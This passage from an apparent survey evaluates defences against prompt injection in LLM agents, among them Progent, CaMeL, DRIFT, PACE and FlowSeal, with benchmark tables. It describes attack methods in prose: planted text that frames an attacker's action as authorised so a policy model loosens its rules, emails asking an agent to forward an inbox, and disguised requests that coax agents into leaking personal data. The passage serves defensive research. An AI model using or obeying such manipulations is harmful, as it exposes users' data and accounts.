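A defence can decide which tool calls a task needs instead of tracing influence. *Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) describes a reference monitor that checks each call against written rules about the tool's name and arguments. A rule might allow Slack messages only to Maya. Rules that forbid a call take priority over rules that allow it, and Progent blocks any call that matches no rule.

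A language model writes the first set of rules from the user's request and proposes changes as the agent learns more. Suppose Maya asks her agent to do what Tom's to-do email says:

| Event | Proposed change to the rules | Progent's response |
|---|---|---|
| Maya makes the request | Allow a search for Tom's email | Uses this as the first policy |
| Tom's email asks for a summary of recent mail, posted to Maya's Slack | Also allow reading mail, looking up Slack names and posting to Slack | Asks for approval |
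| The lookup returns Maya's Slack name | Allow Slack posts only to Maya | Applies the change |
| A stranger's email asks the agent to forward the inbox | Allow sending email | Asks for approval |

Let A(P) be the set of calls that policy P allows. A new policy P′ takes effect automatically only if

A(P′) ⊆ A(P)

A solver, a conventional program that checks logical formulas, decides whether this holds. A manipulated model therefore can't widen the agent's privileges without approval.

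Progent does not record whose text led to a call or supplied its arguments. Between the second and third rows, the agent may post to anyone on Slack, so a stranger's text that arrived then could determine the recipient. It could also lead the model to narrow the rule to the stranger's account, and the solver would accept that as a reduction in privileges. Shi and colleagues exclude attacks that stay within what the task needs and those that only change the agent's written answer.

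The protection also depends on who approves changes to the rules. *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) warns that a poisoned tool result may cause an update to loosen the rules. The solver detects the loosening, but the update still takes effect if the owner has turned on automatic approval.

Shi and colleagues used that setting as a worst case in their main test. On AgentDojo with GPT-4o, attack success fell from 39.9 percent to 1.0 percent while the agent remained about as useful. With the first policy fixed, the rate was 2.5 percent. When a person reviewed the first policy and each expansion, no attack succeeded. Only 6 percent of updates were expansions, so this review would not often interrupt an owner on tasks like AgentDojo's.

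### An attacker who knows the rules

Adaptive attackers have defeated most defences that rely on a model recognising or resisting planted text. In June 2026, Narisetty and colleagues tested whether Progent, which enforces its rules outside the model, would resist them better. Progent still uses a model to rewrite its policy, so they attacked that step. Their text described the attacker's action as harmless, necessary and already authorised by the user, in the hope that the model would add it to the rules.

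The agent was Qwen2.5-7B, a small open model, which also wrote Progent's policies. The researchers used eight user tasks from each of three AgentDojo settings, paired each task with every attack in its setting, and ran the whole test three times.

| Setting | Attack success, no defence | Attack success, Progent | Attack success, Progent with the adaptive attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| Banking | 19.0% | 1.9% | 3.7% |
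| Slack | 58.3% | 10.8% | 4.2% |
| Office workspace | 0.0% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| Mean | 25.8% | 4.2% | 2.6% |

The adaptive attack was less successful on average than the standard one. Narisetty and colleagues think the polite wording they wrote for the policy model also made the agent less likely to obey. They didn't run the adaptive attack against an undefended agent, so the result could reflect either a strong defence or a weak attack. The office tasks provide no evidence about Progent, because the small model ignored the planted instructions there even without a defence.

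Progent reduced the share of tasks completed under attack from 45.2 percent to 27.1 percent, and to 25.8 percent when the attack was adaptive. It also needed about 15 times as many model calls per task. The completion rate did not fall for banking tasks, but it fell by about half for Slack and office tasks. A stronger model might write better policies, but it might also carry out an attacker's instructions more competently.

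This evidence is encouraging but limited. The test covered one weak model and one attack template, and the researchers did not try automated optimisation or an attack that uses only calls the policy already allows. They work for LaunchSafe, which builds security tools for agents on the same principle, so they have an interest in the result. They acknowledge most of these limits and say the test does not establish that defences outside the model are harder to beat. Progent's developers had reported similar rates, from about 0.5 to 4.2 percent, for their adaptive attacks with GPT-4o.

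### Assigning the first label

Progent avoids provenance labels, but most of the other designs depend on them, and Narisetty and colleagues argue that no system they surveyed adequately specifies how to assign the first label. Combining labels is simple arithmetic, but somebody first has to decide which email header to believe, which part of a message the user pasted from elsewhere, and which other agent a text came through.

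Most tests skip this step because the testers supply the labels, as Costa and colleagues did on AgentDojo. Cai and colleagues gave both detectors TaintBench's own list of untrusted and consequential tools. In *Taming Various Privilege Escalation in LLM-Based Agent Systems*, Ji, Wu and colleagues (2026) label each agent, tool and database in advance and assume that the tools come from a trusted supplier. They report that no attack succeeded on AgentDojo or another fixed benchmark, InjecAgent. But if a whole mail tool had one label, Tom's email and a stranger's would get the same label.

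Narisetty and colleagues propose that future tests include attackers who try to get their text mislabeled. They might forge a sender's address or persuade Maya to paste a paragraph into her request. Both attacks can succeed even if the rule that checks the label works correctly, so a test that starts from correct labels can't measure the risk.

### Tasks that change as the agent works

Fixed plans and narrow rules suit tasks whose steps are clear from the start. In *AgentDyn*, Li, Wen and colleagues (2026) count only 6 of AgentDojo's 97 tasks that require the agent to change its plan along the way. Their benchmark has 60 tasks in shopping, GitHub and daily life, and 560 combinations of a task with an attack. The tasks average 7.1 steps, about twice as many as AgentDojo's, and give the agent more tools.

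Each task also includes a helpful instruction from a third party that the agent has to follow. For example, a bank may refuse a payment above $500 until the agent finds a one-time code in the user's inbox and enters it. A system that treats every instruction in a tool result as an attack can't complete such a payment.

The researchers tested CaMeL, Progent and DRIFT. *DRIFT* (2025) combines rules from an initial plan with a model that can permit departures from that plan. The table shows the share of tasks completed when there was no attack and the share of attacks that succeeded.

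| System | Tasks, GPT-4o | Attacks, GPT-4o | Tasks, Gemini 2.5 Pro | Attacks, Gemini 2.5 Pro |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| No defence | 53.3% | 37.8% | 51.7% | 20.6% |
| CaMeL | 0.0% | 0.0% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| Progent | 6.7% | 1.7% | 25.0% | 1.6% |
| DRIFT | 30.0% | 0.8% | 36.7% | 1.1% |

Li and colleagues blame CaMeL's failure on its fixed program, which can't add steps the agent discovers later. Progent had trouble choosing the right permissions from a large set of tools, and its mistakes accumulated until it blocked almost every useful call. DRIFT was more flexible but still depended on its first plan.

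The size of these losses is less certain. CaMeL needs policies written for each set of tools, and *AutoDojo* (2026) left it out of a later test on AgentDyn for that reason. The same paper classes 18 of the 60 tasks as fully specified by the user. A fixed program might have completed a few of those, so missing policies may partly explain CaMeL's score of zero. *Evolution Under Fire* (2026) also ran Progent on AgentDyn and kept its policy updates off, because that is the default in the released software. If Li and colleagues used the same default, they tested Progent without the feature meant for tasks that change along the way. Some of them had also helped develop DRIFT, which did better than CaMeL and Progent.

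The benchmark also gives little credit for caution. Li and colleagues told the agents to finish every task without asking the user for confirmation, which several of these defences rely on. In one scenario, a friend emails her shopping account's password and asks the agent to use it to buy a light bulb. Many owners would want the agent to check with them first.

AgentDyn is a better test of usefulness than of security, as its creators acknowledge. Without any defence, Claude Sonnet 4.5 completed 71.7 percent of the tasks. The standard attack succeeded against it 0.9 percent of the time, and an attack that the researchers adapted to the scenarios succeeded 3.0 percent of the time. Given these figures, an owner might reasonably choose the newer model without a defence over CaMeL with an older model, although there is no guarantee that the newer model would resist a better attack.

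### PACE: checking paths and effects

*PACE* (Li, Wang and colleagues, October 2026) reported much smaller losses on the same benchmark. PACE makes two checks on each tool call just before it runs. The path check looks for a route in the provenance record from untrusted or secret data to a harmful effect, and selects a way to cut it, usually by blocking the call. The effect check lists what the call would do and compares this with what the user's authenticated request authorizes. This second check resembles the grants that Wei and Xiong propose.

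With GPT-5.6 Luna on AgentDyn, PACE completed 73.6 percent of tasks, compared with 74.8 percent for an undefended agent, and reduced attack success from 19.5 percent to zero. Across eight benchmarks and three models, it had the lowest attack rate in 62 of 79 comparisons and tied for the lowest in 14. The researchers wrote policies and tool descriptions for each benchmark beforehand, so an owner would need comparable policies and descriptions for their own tools.

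The researchers also turned parts of PACE on and off in a smaller test with Qwen-3.8-27B. For the last row, they added a component that can repair calls or restore blocked ones.

| Parts turned on | Attacks, AgentDojo | Tasks, AgentDojo | Attacks, AgentDyn | Tasks, AgentDyn |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 37.4% | 76.8% | 25.0% | 66.7% |
| Path check | 0.0% | 13.6% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| Effect check | 0.0% | 64.6% | 1.7% | 36.7% |
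| Both checks | 0.0% | 65.2% | 1.7% | 36.7% |
| Complete system | 0.0% | 67.2% | 0.0% | 33.3% |

The path check, a content-tracking rule, stopped all useful work on AgentDyn when used alone. Most of the practical benefit came from the effect check, which depends on what Maya authorised and not on whose text influenced the agent. The complete system also halved the number of completed AgentDyn tasks in this smaller test, although the same model lost only about three percentage points on the full benchmark. The paper notes that the smaller test used a different mix of tasks, but such a large difference needs a fuller explanation.

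PACE was also tested against an adaptive attacker that could make up to 50 attempts on each of 30 AgentDojo cases. The attacker succeeded in 21 cases against the undefended agent and in none against PACE. All 30 targets were outside the user's authority, so the effect check should catch them. An attacker who changed the amount of a payment that Maya had authorised would be a harder test.

The paper's security proof does not fully cover the system that produced these results. The certified version has to keep every cut that the path check requires, but the tested version can restore a blocked call if the effect check approves it, which reopens the route from untrusted data. Even for the certified version, the proof covers only routes that appear in the provenance record. It doesn't apply if the model rebuilds a secret in its own words or a tool has a side effect missing from its description.

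### Records labelled with permitted recipients

Some leaks need no planted instruction at all. In September 2026, Shim, Karim and colleagues, in *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (2026), studied people who simply ask an agent for information about someone else, as Aditya asked Ash for other people's emails. Their attackers made the request look like ordinary work:

- One invited the agent to fill in its part of a shared page.
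- Another listed real and invented facts about a person and asked the agent to delete the false ones, so that the entries left on the page revealed the truth.
- A third put the request in an email and collected the answer on a separate page.

A detailed prompt instructed the agent to verify identities and get the data owner's consent before sharing data. With this prompt in place, earlier attacks had extracted at most 3 percent of the sensitive items. The new attacks extracted 52.2, 75.6 and 43.8 percent respectively, because the agent didn't recognise them as requests for information.

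The researchers' defence, FlowSeal, labels each record with its owner and the people who may receive it. A summary of two records can go only to people allowed to receive both. A program outside the agent checks every call that writes or shares something. If the recipient isn't already approved, a separate model compares the protected records with the proposed text and returns SAFE or BLOCKED. The three leak rates fell to 0.5, 2.3 and 2.2 percent. FlowSeal completed 72.4 percent of ordinary tasks, close to the best prompt-based defence's 75.9 percent.

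Both security and task completion depend on the separate model's answers. When the researchers replaced its answer with BLOCKED every time, the leak rate in the shared-page attack was 1.3 percent, but the agent completed none of the ordinary tasks. When they replaced it with SAFE every time, the agent completed 79.4 percent of those tasks and leaked 24.9 percent of the items. The paper proves that protected data can't reach an unauthorised recipient unless this model wrongly answers SAFE. An attacker would try to cause that mistake, and nobody has yet tested an attacker who knows how the model works. Shim and colleagues themselves suggest one possible attack, which would split a fact across several messages that each look harmless.

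FlowSeal also withheld information it should have shared. In a test where the owner would consent if asked, it delivered 32.7 percent of the requested items, while the four prompt-based defences delivered 61 to 86 percent. The 72.4 percent figure for ordinary tasks does not reflect this weakness, because those tasks did not involve requests for sensitive information.

### What an attack rate and a proof can establish

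These tests measure different things. NeuroTaint's score measures how well a detector explains actions that have already happened, so even a perfect score would not mean that any were prevented. An adaptive attack test measures how often one kind of attacker succeeds. AgentDyn mainly measures how much useful work an agent can still do with a defense in place, and CaMeL stopped every attack there but completed no tasks.

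An attack rate reflects the whole running system, including software bugs and the model's own caution, so it can reveal problems that a proof assumes are absent. But it is an average over the attacks that the testers chose, and real attackers choose the text most likely to work and can keep trying. Even for attacks like those in the *PACE* test, zero successes in 30 cases is consistent with a true rate of up to about 11 percent, according to the paper's 95 percent interval.

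A soundness proof can cover every text an attacker might write, but only for the property it states, under its assumptions, and for the version of the system it describes. A sound system can still have a nonzero attack success rate, as CaMeL did on AgentDojo, where one successful injection was of a kind that CaMeL's developers don't claim to stop.

Proofs and benchmarks can both miss a wrong initial label. Suppose the developer of Maya's agent marks her calendar as trusted, forgetting that strangers can send her invitations. A proof that assumes correct labels still holds, and a benchmark without attacks in calendar entries still gives an attack success rate of zero. To find the mistake, someone has to check who can write to each field in each of the agent's tools.
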